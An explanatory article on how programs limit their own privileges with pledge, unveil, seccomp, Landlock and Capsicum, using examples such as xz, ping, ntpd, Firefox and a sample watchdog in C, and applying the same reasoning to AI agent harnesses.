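# How software limits itself in advance, and when outside enforcement is still needed

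## What it means for a program to bind itself

In computer security, self-binding means writing a program so that it gives up powers before it does anything risky. The operating system then denies it those powers for as long as it runs, so a later bug, break-in or bad instruction does less harm. Web browsers, login servers and hundreds of small command-line tools work this way. Since 2025, so do some AI agents, which are programs where a language model chooses the actions and ordinary software carries them out.

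A decompressor such as xz reads a compressed file and writes out the original, and it never needs the network. But compressed formats are complicated, and someone who finds a mistake in the decoding code may be able to build a file that makes xz run instructions hidden inside it. Those instructions can do whatever xz can do, which on an ordinary system includes reading the user's private keys and sending them to a stranger's server. So the developer adds a step, before xz reads the file, that tells the operating system to deny xz network access from then on. A malicious file may still take over xz, but it can no longer send anything over the network.

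A process is a running program with its own memory. The kernel is the core of the operating system, and it controls files, memory, processes and the network. To use any of these, a process makes a system call, which is a request to the kernel, for example to open a file or connect to a server. Kerrisk (2023) points out in *Seccomp* that Linux has about 400 system calls and that most programs use only a small subset. If a program makes a call outside that subset, an attacker may well have compromised it.

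A privilege is a power that the kernel lets a process use. By default, a process gets roughly the privileges of the person who started it, whatever the program is for, which is the only reason a decompressor can open network connections. A sandbox is a restricted environment in which a process can reach only some files, network addresses or system calls. In *Landlock*, an article on the Linux sandboxing mechanism he wrote, Salaün compares sandboxing with an older job of operating systems, keeping one user's data safe from another user. Sandboxing provides the same protection between the programs of a single user, any of which might start to harm that user.

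### One process at two times

Every such limit involves three roles, which are easy to confuse because the same process fills two of them. The program that requests the limit is xz in its first few milliseconds, running exactly the code that its developer wrote. The enforcer is whatever stops a forbidden action, here the kernel. The later program is xz again, now with the untrusted file in its memory. It may be working perfectly, or it may have hit a bug or be under an attacker's control.

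An AI agent divides in the same way. The harness, which is the ordinary software around the model, can request a limit before the model has read anything. Later, the same harness carries out actions that the model proposed after reading a web page. That page may contain a prompt injection, which is text written to make the model follow someone else's instructions.

Self-binding rests on the assumption that a program does what its developer intended when it sets its own limits, but can't be relied on to do so afterwards. Kerrisk describes a system call filter as a "declaration that we don't trust subsequently executed code", and Salaün assumes that any program, however trusted at first, can become malicious once someone compromises it.

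Self-binding assumes that a program is trustworthy when it requests its limits. This assumption is fairly modest, but it excludes some cases. A program with a backdoor will request no limit or a useless one, so self-binding gives the user no protection. The same is true of a program that reads hostile input before binding itself.

Kernel developers cannot assume that a process requesting a limit is trustworthy. It may already be "compromised or backdoored", as Salaün (2026) puts it in *Landlock LSM*, so the request itself has to be harmless to everyone else. An attacker could block a system call, then start a program that depends on that call and runs with administrator rights, hoping that it misbehaves in a useful way. Before an unprivileged process may limit itself, Linux therefore makes it give up any chance of gaining privileges through the programs it starts.

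### Four conditions for a limit to bind

Suppose an attacker now controls xz and tries to open the forbidden connection. The limit stops the attempt only if the enforcer still works as built, the rule is still in force, the rule applies to whatever is making the attempt, and it covers that kind of attempt.

Once a program has limited itself, it must not be able to change whatever enforces the limit. Suppose the developer of xz doesn't use the kernel and instead writes a variable into the program, `network_allowed = false`, which the program's own networking code checks. An attacker who controls the process can write to its memory, so he can set the variable to true, or he can skip the check and make the system call directly. Saltzer and Schroeder made the same point about hardware in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). They describe a processor with a special register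 that holds the range of memory the current program may use, and note that there would be no protection if any running program could load any value into that register. Their solution is an extra bit in the processor that is on only while the supervisor program, today the kernel, is running. The register can change only while that bit is on.

The program must also be unable to undo the limit later. Kernels ensure this by letting each request only remove permissions. If a process may take the actions in a set A and requests a limit to the set R, it keeps only the actions in both, A ∩ R, and no later request can enlarge that set. According to OpenBSD's manual page *pledge(2)*, a program can drop further groups of operations but cannot reactivate the ones it has dropped. Linux's Landlock likewise allows only additions to the restrictions on a process, according to its user documentation (Salaün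 2026, *Landlock*). Because a process can only lose powers this way, it is reasonable to let any process limit itself without an administrator's permission.

However, the limit lasts only as long as the process. Suppose xz read a configuration file that turned its sandbox on or off, and the sandbox still let xz write to that file. The attacker could change the setting to off. The kernel would keep the network closed until xz exited, but the next time the user started xz, it would not request a limit. Salaün's article warns of such tampering with configuration files and caches. It adds that the kernel may be unable to prevent the tampering or even warn about it, because the kernel has no information about which files matter to a given program.

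A limit can also hold perfectly on the process that requested it while some other part of the program goes uncovered. Salaün gives the example of a process that starts a child process, then sandboxes itself, then starts a second child. The second child inherits the limit. The first has no limit, and if it accepts requests from its parent, an attacker in the parent can have it open the connection. Several other gaps have the same shape:

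- On OpenBSD, a process that has kept the right to run other programs can start one that has no limit, unless it set a limit for new programs beforehand.
- Before version 8 of its interface, Landlock limited only the thread that made the request and that thread's children. Threads are parts of one process that run side by side and share its memory, so an attacker could simply work through a neighbouring thread.
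- Seccomp, the Linux mechanism that filters system calls, has trouble with debuggers. A process that can attach to another as a debugger may be able to swap one system call for a different one after the filter has checked it, and the Linux kernel documentation's *Seccomp BPF (SECure COMPuting with filters)* warns sandbox authors not to allow this without extreme care.

Saltzer and Schroeder call the general requirement complete mediation, meaning that the system must check every access to every object. They are suspicious of systems that remember the result of an earlier check. Landlock remembers some results by design. It decides most rights to a file when a process opens it, so xz keeps those rights to any file it opened before binding itself.

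Finally, the enforcer's rules must be able to express the restriction. A seccomp filter receives the system call's number and raw arguments. When a program opens a file, the filter receives the memory address of the file's name but cannot read the name stored there. Seccomp therefore cannot restrict a program to opening one particular file, but Landlock can. Landlock's network rules, however, refer to port numbers, not server names, so a program that should contact only its own update server can at best limit itself to the port that server uses, which many other servers also use.

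Landlock has been able to block TCP connections since version 4 of its interface, but it gained rules for UDP, the other common way of sending data, only recently, in version 10. On an older kernel, if the xz decompressor had relied on Landlock alone to block network access, it could still have leaked the user's keys in UDP packets, with no visible sign of a problem. The documentation recommends that programs drop any restrictions the running kernel does not support and apply the rest. This is sensible for software that has to run everywhere, but it means that the same program binds itself more loosely on some machines than on others.

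The gap between the rule one wants and the rule one can state is wider for AI agents. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes a browser agent that works through clicks and keystrokes. Its user asks it to comment on one numbered issue on GitLab, a site for managing software projects. It is easy to say in words that the agent may visit that issue, write in the comment box, and touch nothing else in the user's account. But that limit is close to meaningless in terms of clicks and keystrokes, because the same click can post a comment or delete a project, depending on what is on the screen.

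### Who writes the limit, and whether anything enforces it

In the xz example, the list of permitted actions ships inside the program, which makes it an embedded policy. In an older arrangement on Linux, the machine's administrator writes the list by configuring SELinux or AppArmor, two access control systems in the kernel, with rules for particular programs. The kernel enforces the policy in both arrangements, but they differ in who writes it and how much the writer knows when writing it.

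Salaün argues for embedding the policy in the program because administrators write their policies apart from any actual run, and so have to make them too broad. In his example, a profile written ahead of time must let a picture viewer read the whole Pictures folder, since nobody can tell which picture the user will open. Once the viewer has seen the file name on its command line, it can limit itself to read-only access to that picture, plus access to its own cache. Embedding also lets the developer who changes the program change the policy in the same edit and test the two together.

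The administrator's policy is still needed, partly because self-binding is voluntary, as the kernel developer Kees Cook stresses about both pledge and seccomp in *evolution of seccomp* (2015). Many developers never do it. An outside policy also survives attacks that an embedded one does not. In Salaün's example, an exploit hidden in the viewer's cache might stop the viewer from sandboxing itself at the next launch, but the restrictions set by the login session and the launcher would still hold. Linux lets the two kinds of policy stack, and an access goes through only if every layer allows it.

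An embedded policy also depends on the developer knowing what the program will do, which is easy for a decompressor. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that an agent has no fixed program to analyse, and often no statement of intent beyond the sentence the user has just typed. The developer of the harness can still ship a list of permitted actions, but it must be broad enough to cover tasks that nobody has thought of yet.

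Both arrangements differ from a rule that exists only as an instruction. A coding guideline may forbid xz to use the network, and a model's prompt may forbid an agent to do the same. Only the program or model that the rule is supposed to limit can enforce it, so anyone who gains control of that program or model also controls whether the rule is followed. Training does not remove this weakness. Christodorescu and colleagues write that a model trained never to do something will comply with some probability, which depends on what the model is reading. They imagine a guard that correctly denies 99% of unauthorised requests. If the attempts were independent, an attacker with a hundred tries would get through at least once with probability 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. Real attackers do better because they search for inputs that work.

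Kernels have security holes too. *Pledge*, part of isopenbsdsecu.re's outside review of OpenBSD's defences, mentions a bypass disclosed by the researcher Alfredo Ortega. An attacker with full administrator rights could place links in the system's time zone directory, which restricted programs could still read, and reach other files through them. A developer can find and fix a defect like that at a particular place in the code, but a model's 1% failure rate has no such location.

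### From least privilege to coding agents

A program that binds itself follows the principle of least privilege, one of eight design principles in Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 paper. The principle is that a program should hold only the powers its task needs, mainly to limit the damage from an accident or error. In their examples, a supervisor imposes the limits. In 2005, Linux added seccomp, which lets a process limit itself. Its original mode allowed only four system calls. Opening a file was not one of them, so a program had to open every file it needed before entering that mode. In July 2012, Linux added filters, which let a program choose its own list of calls.

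In July 2015 Theo de Raadt, who leads OpenBSD, proposed a simpler call named tame. gihyo.jp's *OpenBSD 5.9の新しいセキュリティ機能pledge(2)* quotes his complaint that one family of existing tools, such as FreeBSD's Capsicum, required a major rewrite of the application. The project had started with a program much like the decompressor, a developer's new version of `file`, which identifies a file's type. According to OpenBSD's slides, its sandbox alone took 300 lines of code with the tool then available. De Raadt renamed tame to pledge that October, and by mid-November 368 of the system's commands used it. In `cat`, which prints files, the call took a single short statement.

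In slides from 2018, OpenBSD's developers presented unveil, a companion call that limits which files a program can see. Landlock reached Linux in 2021, after more than five years of work and 34 versions of the code (Corbet, 2021, *Landlock (finally) sets sail*). Since 2025, developers of coding agents, which write software and run commands on the user's machine, have used these kernel mechanisms to limit what the commands chosen by a model can do.

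## Dividing the program and choosing the moment to bind

A developer who wants to limit a program first has to know what the program uses and when. Most programs need wide powers for a moment at the start, while they read their settings and open their files. This is the setup phase. In the working phase that follows, the program handles untrusted input and mostly repeats a few actions. A single limit for the whole run would have to allow everything that either phase needs, so the developer separates the phases before writing any policy:

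1. List everything the program touches, including files, network connections, devices and other programs that it starts.
2. Mark each item as belonging to the setup phase, the working phase or both.
3. Move one-time work to the front. Open files and sockets there (a socket is a program's end of a network connection) and keep them open.
4. Bind the program, and only then read untrusted input.

Opening files before binding helps because the process keeps its access to them afterward. It holds a file descriptor for each open file, which is a handle for reading or writing it. A process that has already opened its log for writing can give up the power to open files and still write to the log.

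*Privilege drop, privilege separation, and restricted-service operating mode in OpenBSD* (2023), an essay by the developer of several OpenBSD background services, describes how `ping`, which tests whether another machine answers, came to limit its own rights. `ping` needs a special kind of socket that only root, the administrator's account, may open, so it used to run with root's rights no matter who started it. In the 1990s de Raadt made `ping` open that socket before reading its command-line options, and drop root's rights immediately afterwards. The options are untrusted input because any user can type them and the program starts with more rights than that user has. Twenty years later the developers noticed that `ping` still ran as root after the drop if root had started it, so they made it switch to an account of its own.

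A program that binds too late receives some hostile input while it still has its setup powers. If it binds too early, the kernel blocks its own setup work, and the developer may respond by adding the setup powers to the permitted list. The program then works, so it is easy to miss that an attacker who later takes it over will have those powers too.

Systrace, an older OpenBSD tool, could apply a policy from outside the program. The policy covered the run from its first instruction, so, as the 2023 essay explains, the program kept every privilege it had needed to start. A program that restricts itself can wait to do so until it has read its options. For example, `ping` keeps the ability to look up host names only if its options require it.

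Developers are still finding work that a program can do earlier, before it limits itself. On 30 September 2026, a developer removed a permission from rpki-client, a program that checks internet routing data. The permission covered connections to other programs on the same machine, and the change log explains, "Now that we open early we can remove unix pledge" (OpenBSD, 2026).

A program can also restrict itself more than once. Beck's *Pledge, and Unveil, in OpenBSD* describes how the network tool `nc` starts with a generous list of permissions and narrows it once it knows which operation the user wants. Some mechanisms make this less convenient. In *Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems*, Alhindi and Hallett (2024) searched the packages of four operating systems and found a library, lowdown, that limits itself in two stages with pledge. Under FreeBSD's Capsicum, lowdown has only the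 later stage, so its early work runs without limits.

### A watchdog, phase by phase

One example is a small watchdog program that runs in the background. It reads its settings, then checks once a minute whether a port (a numbered entry point for connections) on a remote server is open, and logs the result. When the log grows too large, the watchdog renames it and starts a new one. Researchers at the University of Bristol used a similar program in a usability study.

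| What the watchdog touches | Setup phase | Working phase |
|---|---|---|
| Settings file | Open, read, close | Nothing |
| Log file | Open for appending, create if missing | Write through the open handle, check the size |
| Log directory | Find the log | Rename the full log, create a new one |
| Server's name | Nothing | Look up the address |
| Port on the server | Nothing | Open a new connection for each check |
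| Clock | Nothing | Read the time, wait for the next check |
| User's other files, other programs, incoming connections | Nothing | Nothing |

The watchdog should bind before it looks up the server's name. The answer to a lookup is untrusted input, since it comes from the network, and code inside the watchdog has to decode it. If the lookup came before binding, a malicious answer would reach a process that could still open any of the user's files. Doing the lookup during setup and keeping the address would let the watchdog give up lookups altogether, but it would also go on testing the old address if the server moved.

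The watchdog can't make its connection before limiting itself, because making the connection is the test. It therefore keeps the power to connect to other machines, and an attacker who takes it over can use that power to send data out. The limits on files stop the attacker from opening the user's private keys, but he can still read and send anything left in the watchdog's memory, including a password if the settings contained one.

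The watchdog may rename its log only once a month, but to do so it must keep permission to create and rename files for the whole run. The developer can limit that permission to the log directory, but an attacker could still destroy old logs there. Alternatively, the system's scheduler can start a new watchdog for every check. Each run would then rename the log if necessary before it used the network, and afterwards would only append to a file it already had open.

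OpenBSD's time daemon, a background service that keeps the computer's clock right, has a similar problem with the file where it records the clock's drift, which it must update as it runs. In the source code (Brauer and Miller, 2020, *ntpd.c*), the daemon opens this file before it binds, then overwrites it through the same handle. It never has to rename or reopen anything, so it can give up the ability to open files for writing. A watchdog that overwrote its oldest results in a log of fixed size could do the same.

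### Privilege separation in the time daemon

Dividing a program into phases doesn't help when it needs a dangerous power and untrusted input at the same time. For as long as it runs, the time daemon must both read packets from servers on the internet and set the clock, and only root may set the clock. Its developers therefore used privilege separation, splitting the program into several processes that each hold only the powers their own part needs.

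The original design, in slides from OpenBSD, had two processes. A parent ran as root. A network process ran under an account with few rights, confined to an empty directory, and asked the parent to adjust the clock and look up server names. The developers later gave name lookup a process of its own. In the 2020 source code the division works roughly like this:

1. The parent starts as root, reads the configuration and starts the network process, with a private channel between the two. It then opens the drift file and binds itself.
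2. The network process sends the name of a time server to the lookup process, which returns the addresses. Before its main loop, the lookup process has dropped root's rights and pledged `stdio dns`, as Brauer (2020), in *ntp_dns.c*, shows. `stdio` covers basic work with handles that are already open, and `dns` covers name lookups.
3. The network process polls the time servers and works out how far the clock is off. According to Beck, its pledge is `stdio inet`, so it can use the network but cannot open files or set the clock.
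4. The network process sends the parent a message containing one number, the correction. The parent checks the message's length, exits if the length is wrong, and otherwise adjusts the clock.

An attacker who takes over the network process with a malicious packet gains no access to files and no root privileges. To go further, he has to attack the parent through the channel between them, where corrections have a fixed size and so leave very little code to exploit. He can still send a wrong correction, and the parent's code does not check whether it is plausible, so the split protects the clock less well than the rest of the computer.

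The parent's list, `stdio rpath inet settime proc exec id`, is longer than its children's. Most of it supports an extra check that Moerbeek describes in *Bootstrapping time on OpenBSD*. The daemon asks a few well-known web servers for the time over an encrypted connection and uses their answers to filter out bad replies from time servers. The parent loads the certificates for these connections and starts a separate process for each one. That process drops its rights and moves into an empty directory before it contacts anyone. The parent can hold wide powers with less risk because other processes communicate with the outside world.

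Dividing a program in the wrong place gives powers to the wrong process. In 2015 the network process started the processes for the web check, so it had to keep the power to create new processes. In a source comment preserved by OpenBSD, a developer called this unfortunate and suggested moving the job to the parent process, and a later change moved it there.

Processes can also pass each other open handles. OpenBSD's `file` utility, which identifies file types, uses this to separate opening a file from looking inside it. According to the 2023 essay's account of the program's four pledges, the parent can open files for reading but never examines their contents. It passes each handle to a child, which decodes the contents but can't open anything itself. An attacker who exploits the decoder with a malicious file therefore controls a process that can read only what the parent hands it. The parent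 could open the user's private keys, but it couldn't send them anywhere because neither process has network access.

Sometimes the parent is hard to limit. OpenBSD's DHCP client, which gets the computer an address on a network, must open a special socket whenever a new network interface needs one, and no pledge permits that. Its developers therefore left the parent, which runs as root, without a pledge. They used unveil to limit its view of the file system to the configuration file, one device and the directory for its records, and kept untrusted data away from it. They also make each child start the program afresh, because a copy of the parent would have the same memory layout, and a leak from one process would help an attacker break into another.

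### Chrome and Firefox

Chrome's developers had already divided the browser into processes when pledge appeared, and OpenBSD's developers reported that they had pledged it strongly in less than a week. Beck lists the pledges for five types of process. The type that renders web pages can read files, but it cannot write them, open network connections or start programs. Pledge could take away kinds of operation, but it could not restrict which files Chrome read. Beck points out that Chrome could still read his SSH keys, which unlock his accounts on other machines. Unveil was meant to add that restriction. Iridium, a browser built from Chrome's open-source code, now has both kinds of limit for each category of process on OpenBSD, according to openports.pl's *The www/iridium port*.

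Restricting Firefox on OpenBSD took years. *Taming the fox* (Breuil, 2022), a set of slides by the developer who maintains Firefox for OpenBSD, gives the usual advice to open devices early and bind as close as possible to the main loop, then adds "in theory... practice is different". The code was too large for him to move big pieces of setup work forward, so he put the OpenBSD calls where Firefox already started its sandboxes for other systems. The main process ended up with 23 promises, OpenBSD's term for groups of permitted operations, including reading, writing and creating files, using the network, and starting other programs. Firefox has had pledge by default since May 2018 and unveil since December 2019.

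Breuil himself called the promises "somewhat wide" and blamed code not written with sandboxing in mind. Mozilla, which develops Firefox, likewise writes that the browser "was not originally designed to be sandboxed". According to the outside review by isopenbsdsecu.re, Firefox's rules allowed pretty much everything, as one would expect of large programs from outside OpenBSD, because the project can't keep rewriting other people's code to suit pledge.

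That verdict fits the main process better than the helpers. According to Breuil's slides, the process for network sockets needs only network access and name lookups beyond the four promises that every Firefox process has, although Firefox then used it only for video calls. On Linux, Mozilla added restrictions to the web-page process in four cumulative levels. According to Mozilla's *Security/Sandbox*, these block the creation of processes, then most file writes, then most file reads, and finally the network. Releases have used the fourth level since Firefox 60. Mozilla could remove these powers because it had moved the code that needed them into other processes.

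Firefox on OpenBSD is still in this mixed state. The notes for version 140.6 in openports.pl's *The www/firefox-esr port* describe separate limits for six types of process, with downloads allowed only into `~/Downloads` and `/tmp`. Screen sharing requires turning off pledge for the main process altogether. The limits are partly an outside policy because they are stored in files under `/etc`, which an administrator can edit but an ordinary user's browser cannot.

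These files also need upkeep. In April 2026, a new OpenBSD user posted a log from Firefox 147 in which the kernel rejected the pledges for two helper processes as invalid (Paul, 2026). Firefox could not start its media decoders, and the user had trouble with YouTube. The likely cause was a mismatch between the files and a newer version of the system. The failure was at least safe, because the decoders did not run without their limits.

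### Servers that have to start other programs

gmid is a small server for Gemini, a simpler alternative to the web. It sends out files and can also run scripts that generate pages. Polo (2021), in *Comparing sandboxing techniques*, describes how he added limits to it on three operating systems. It was a single process, and that became a problem on Linux and FreeBSD, where seccomp and Capsicum limits pass to every process that a limited process starts. A script might need to open a database or contact another server, and under gmid's own limits it would fail.

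So Polo split gmid in two. A listener accepts connections and restricts itself, while an executor stays outside the sandbox and runs scripts when the listener requests them. On OpenBSD, a pledge does not normally carry over to a newly started program, so he could limit the executor as well.

Alhindi and Hallett counted 549 lines of code for seccomp, 96 for pledge and unveil together, and 28 for Capsicum. These figures give some indication of the developer's work but little of the protection. Capsicum needed so few lines partly because gmid already opened its files in the way Capsicum requires. Polo only had to switch it on before the main loop, and the 28 lines don't include the work of splitting the server. A seccomp filter has to name system calls one by one, and Polo also wrote debugging code for it. By his estimate, the result was half as long as the whole first version of gmid.

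The OpenBSD count of 96 lines covers both processes, while the other two counts cover only the listener. Alhindi and Hallett conclude that pledge and unveil gave gmid the more secure sandbox. The advantage is modest, because an attacker who controls the executor can still start programs that have no limits.

A longer filter is not always tighter. The seccomp filter in arping, a network testing tool, allows just 9 system calls, while a single pledge promise, `stdio`, allows 69. But the developer of xwallpaper, which sets the desktop background, copied the same 69 calls by hand into a seccomp filter.

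A program may also need to start a fresh copy of itself. In *pledge with a reëxecing process*, tedu (2025) describes a web application that he restarted every day to add features. To avoid dropping connections, he made the server replace itself with the new version while keeping its listening socket open. Because a restart is a second setup phase, the server had to keep the power to create processes and run programs the whole time it was serving untrusted clients.

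Unveil let the server run only its own program file, but an attacker could still restart it with different options, such as naming `/etc/passwd`, the system's list of accounts, as the log file. tedu had mostly convinced himself that such an attack was unlikely, then decided that anyone who uses pledge cares about unlikely attacks. He moved the web application into a worker process, which the main process starts and which gives up the ability to run programs. Including a helper that already existed, the server now has three processes, and he thinks the code is better organised as a result.

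## Writing the limits with pledge and unveil on OpenBSD

OpenBSD gives developers two system calls for writing limits into a program. The program uses pledge to list the kinds of operation it will still need, and unveil to list the files. The watchdog needs both, because a developer cannot specify individual files with pledge, and unveil has no effect on network access.

### The promises

A program calls pledge with a short string of promises, such as `"stdio rpath"`. The May 2026 manual page from OpenBSD divides the system's operations into about three dozen groups, each with its own promise. After the call, the kernel refuses the process anything outside the groups it listed, and later calls can only drop more groups. Many small programs need only a few of these eight:

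- `stdio` covers work inside the process and on handles that are already open, such as allocating memory, reading the clock and writing to an open file.
- `rpath` lets the process open files for reading and look up details such as their size.
- `wpath` lets it open files for writing.
- `cpath` lets it create and remove files.
- `inet` covers internet connections, both outgoing and incoming.
- `dns` covers looking up server names. The system's C library, the shared code through which programs make most system calls, marks the sockets it opens for lookups. The kernel can therefore allow those and refuse other connections.
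- `proc` lets the process copy itself with a call named `fork`, and send signals to other processes, for example to stop them.
- `exec` lets it replace itself with another program. A process that also has `proc` can fork first, and so start the other program while it continues to run.

The first call to pledge also imposes some limits whatever the string contains. For example, the process can no longer make memory executable unless it has a promise named `prot_exec`. An attacker who takes over the watchdog therefore can't load his own machine code and has to reuse pieces of code that are already there. With an empty string, the process can only exit or compute on memory it shares with another process.

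### Why a violation kills the process

If a process tries something outside its promises, the kernel usually kills it with a signal that the program cannot catch, and saves a copy of its memory for debugging if possible. A few attempts, such as opening the file of encrypted passwords, fail without killing the process.

Killing the process has a drawback. If the watchdog's developer forgot `cpath`, the program could run well for a month and then die the first time it renamed its log, and nobody would notice if the server went down. In the OpenBSD slides *Mitigations and other real security features*, de Raadt argues that continuing would be worse. He rejects the usual idea that robust software recovers from errors, and asks, "If memory has been overwritten, how does one continue?" A forbidden call means that the developer misunderstood the program or that an attacker controls it. A crash stops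 an attack, and it also exposes a mistake so that a user reports it and the developer fixes it. De Raadt describes the pledge string as a second specification, written into the program itself, that lets developers test their assumptions about what the program does.

With the `error` promise, a forbidden system call returns an error code instead of killing the program. When de Raadt introduced it in December 2017, he warned developers to use it with "EXTREME CAUTION", because libraries and programs are full of system calls whose results nobody checks. His email is reproduced in bsdb0y's *openbsd intro to update on pledge*.

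Suppose a server starts as root and then switches to a weaker account, but its developer left out the promise for changing accounts. By default, the kernel kills the server when it tries to switch. With `error`, the switch fails, and if the code ignores the result, the server goes on to handle untrusted input as root. For the same reason, the OpenBSD change that added `error` barred processes from imposing it on programs that run with more rights than the user who starts them. `error` also helps an attacker who is exploring what a process can do, because a forbidden call no longer kills the process.

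### Hiding the file system

Without unveil, a process with `rpath` can read every file that its user can read, so Chrome could still reach Beck's SSH keys. The first call to unveil hides the whole file system from the process except for one path, and later calls add other paths. Each call gives the permissions for its path as letters: `r` for reading, `w` for writing, `x` for running a program, and `c` for creating and removing files. Permissions on a directory apply to everything beneath it, unless another call sets a rule for something deeper. The process still needs the matching promises, so a program without `wpath` can't write to files in a directory even if unveil gives it `w` there.

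OpenBSD's *unveil* manual page strongly recommends locking the list once it is complete. Until then, the process can still add any path to the list, so an attacker who took over the process could add the user's private keys and read them. A program locks the list by calling unveil with two empty arguments, or by calling pledge without the `unveil` promise.

A process that breaks an unveil rule gets an error but is not killed. If it tries to open a hidden file, the kernel usually reports that the file does not exist. If the file is visible but the permission is missing, the kernel reports that access is denied. Many programs look for optional files and already handle these errors. Others misbehave badly when a file they rely on disappears, so the manual suggests that unveiling whole directories is often easier than listing files.

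An unveil rule for a directory applies only to the directory that existed at the time of the call, so if someone deletes and recreates the watchdog's log directory, the new one appears not to exist. A rule for a file applies to the file's name within its directory, so a program can delete and recreate an unveiled file without losing access.

Older tools such as systrace compared the file name in a system call with a list of permitted names before the kernel looked up the file. Anderson's *A comparison of Unix sandboxing techniques* (2017) explains that this fails because another process can change what the name leads to between the check and the lookup, for example by replacing a directory with a link. Beck describes unveil as part of the kernel's own name lookup, where the check and the lookup happen together.

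### The watchdog's limits in C

Suppose the watchdog keeps its settings in `/etc/watchdog.conf` and its logs in a directory of its own. Its limits take three calls:

```c
/* Setup phase */
if (pledge("stdio rpath wpath cpath inet dns unveil", NULL) == -1)
        err(1, "pledge");
read_settings("/etc/watchdog.conf");
open_log("/var/log/watchdog/current");

/* Working phase */
if (unveil("/var/log/watchdog", "rwc") == -1)
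        err(1, "unveil");
if (pledge("stdio rpath wpath cpath inet dns", NULL) == -1)
        err(1, "pledge");
check_port_every_minute();
```

The function `err` prints a message and exits, so the watchdog doesn't run without its limits. The second pledge string drops one word from the first, which locks the list of files. Nearly all the difference between the phases comes from unveil. During setup the watchdog can read any file its account can read, and afterwards it can open files only in the log directory. The developer doesn't have to unveil the system files that name lookup needs, because `dns` includes access to them.

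An attacker who took over the watchdog in its working phase would have these powers left:

| Promise | What the attacker could still do |
|---|---|
| `stdio` | Read everything in the watchdog's memory, write false results to the open log or empty it, and use up processor time |
| `rpath` | Read the old logs |
| `wpath` | Overwrite the old logs |
| `cpath` | Delete the logs, or create files until the disk is full |
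| `inet` | Send data to any server the machine can reach, attack other machines on the local network, or wait for incoming connections |
| `dns` | Send data out disguised as name lookups, which adds little here because `inet` already allows more |

The watchdog has neither `proc` nor `exec`, so if the attacker tries to start a command shell, the kernel kills the watchdog. With `proc`, he could stop other programs running under the same account and make copies of the watchdog until the machine slowed down. With `exec` as well, he could start any program that unveil left executable.

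If the watchdog keeps only one old log, the developer can tighten these limits by unveiling the two file names instead of the directory. The attacker can then damage only those two files. A better solution is for the watchdog not to handle log files at all. `stdio` permits a call that passes a message to the system's logging service. If the watchdog logs that way, the service stores the messages and another program can rotate the files. The working phase then needs only `"stdio inet dns"`, the same string that Beck gives for `ping`, and the watchdog can't open any of the user's files. An attacker could still add false entries to the log but couldn't erase old ones.

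### What a newly started program inherits

A process that copies itself with `fork` passes its limits on to the copy. When a process starts a different program, OpenBSD's manual says the new program runs without any pledge, "and hopefully makes a new pledge soon", unless the process set execpromises beforehand. Execpromises are a second string of promises, already in force when the new program begins. They are the second argument to pledge, which the watchdog leaves as `NULL`. The kernel refuses to start a program under execpromises if it would run with its owner's rights instead of the user's, as `ping` does.

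Anderson, one of the designers of FreeBSD's Capsicum, considered this loss of limits pledge's greatest weakness, but he wrote a few months before OpenBSD added execpromises, which let developers prevent it.

Execpromises can't restrict a new program to particular files. Suppose the watchdog's developer adds a small program that emails an alert when the server goes down. The watchdog now needs `proc` and `exec`, and the developer unveils the alert program with `x` so that the watchdog can run nothing else. Execpromises can stop the alert program from starting other programs, but it starts with no unveils, and the watchdog can't set them in advance. If the alert program needs to read files and use the network, it can also read the user's private keys and send them to someone else. An attacker who controls the watchdog chooses the alert program's arguments, and if one of its options attaches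 a file to the message, the attacker can steal the keys without exploiting another bug. The alert program therefore has to call unveil itself before it acts on its arguments.

Execpromises also bring back systrace's difficulty with setup. They apply from the new program's first instruction, so they must include every power it needs to start. In 2018 Beck called them "not easy to use today" and thought they needed to work together with unveil.

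The new program may also call `pledge` itself. If it requests a promise that its execpromises lack, the call fails, and a carefully written program then exits. The parent can avoid this by including `error` in the execpromises. The kernel then ignores the request but reports success, and the new program continues with fewer powers than it requested. This is convenient for running programs that nobody has adapted, but it carries the risk of unchecked errors described above.

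### Coarse groups and filter programs

De Raadt designed pledge partly in reaction to seccomp filters, small programs that the kernel runs on each system call to decide whether to allow it. In a 2015 message quoted by isopenbsdsecu.re, he objected that developers would have to write a second program to monitor the first, and he called the idea insane. In slides later that year, he added that such a filter is separate from the program and easily gets out of sync with it.

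Kees Cook, who works on seccomp, answered that most of this was a misunderstanding. A filter always halts, the kernel checks it before using it, and a program can include it in its own source code, as it can with a pledge. A filter is likely to stop matching the program only when someone else writes it for a program that does not limit itself. Cook sees the ability to write filters for other people's programs as an advantage of seccomp, because a launcher can then limit programs whose developers never did.

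Cook's corrections are right on the technical points, but they don't refute the practical argument for coarse groups. He granted that few Linux programs had adopted seccomp filters, and that this could be blamed on how fine-grained the filters are. djm, a commenter on his article, gave a stronger reason to prefer groups. Programs reach the kernel mostly through the C library, whose developers may change which system calls it makes. A program that lists individual calls can break when the library starts to use a new one. If the program requests `stdio` instead, the group's maintainers can add the new call and the program keeps working. Cook agreed that getting this mapping right was "the real trick". It is easier on OpenBSD, where one project maintains both the kernel and the library.

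According to an earlier OpenBSD manual, the developers chose the groups mostly by studying the behaviour of many programs. The first proposal, which patrick_g (2015) summarised for French readers in *Tame et OpenBSD*, had different groups. It included a separate permission for allocating memory, which is now part of `stdio`.

Grouping system calls into broad promises makes the limits less precise. A program that only reads from one open handle and writes to another still gets all of the roughly 70 system calls in `stdio`, each leading to kernel code that might contain a bug. The watchdog only makes outgoing connections, but `inet` also lets it accept incoming ones. SerenityOS, another operating system that adopted pledge, divides the groups more finely, though each extra promise makes the list a little harder to learn. awesomekling's *pledge() and unveil() in SerenityOS* describes a separate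 promise, `accept`, for servers that open their listening socket during setup. They can then serve clients without keeping the ability to connect to other machines.

Anderson thought pledge was too imprecise for complex programs. An application that must write to its own private files needs `wpath`, which in 2017 let it write to any file that its user could change. He concluded that pledge would catch mistakes and unskilled attackers but was no basis for a rigorous policy. Programs that use unveil, which was released in 2018, avoid the problem with `wpath`.

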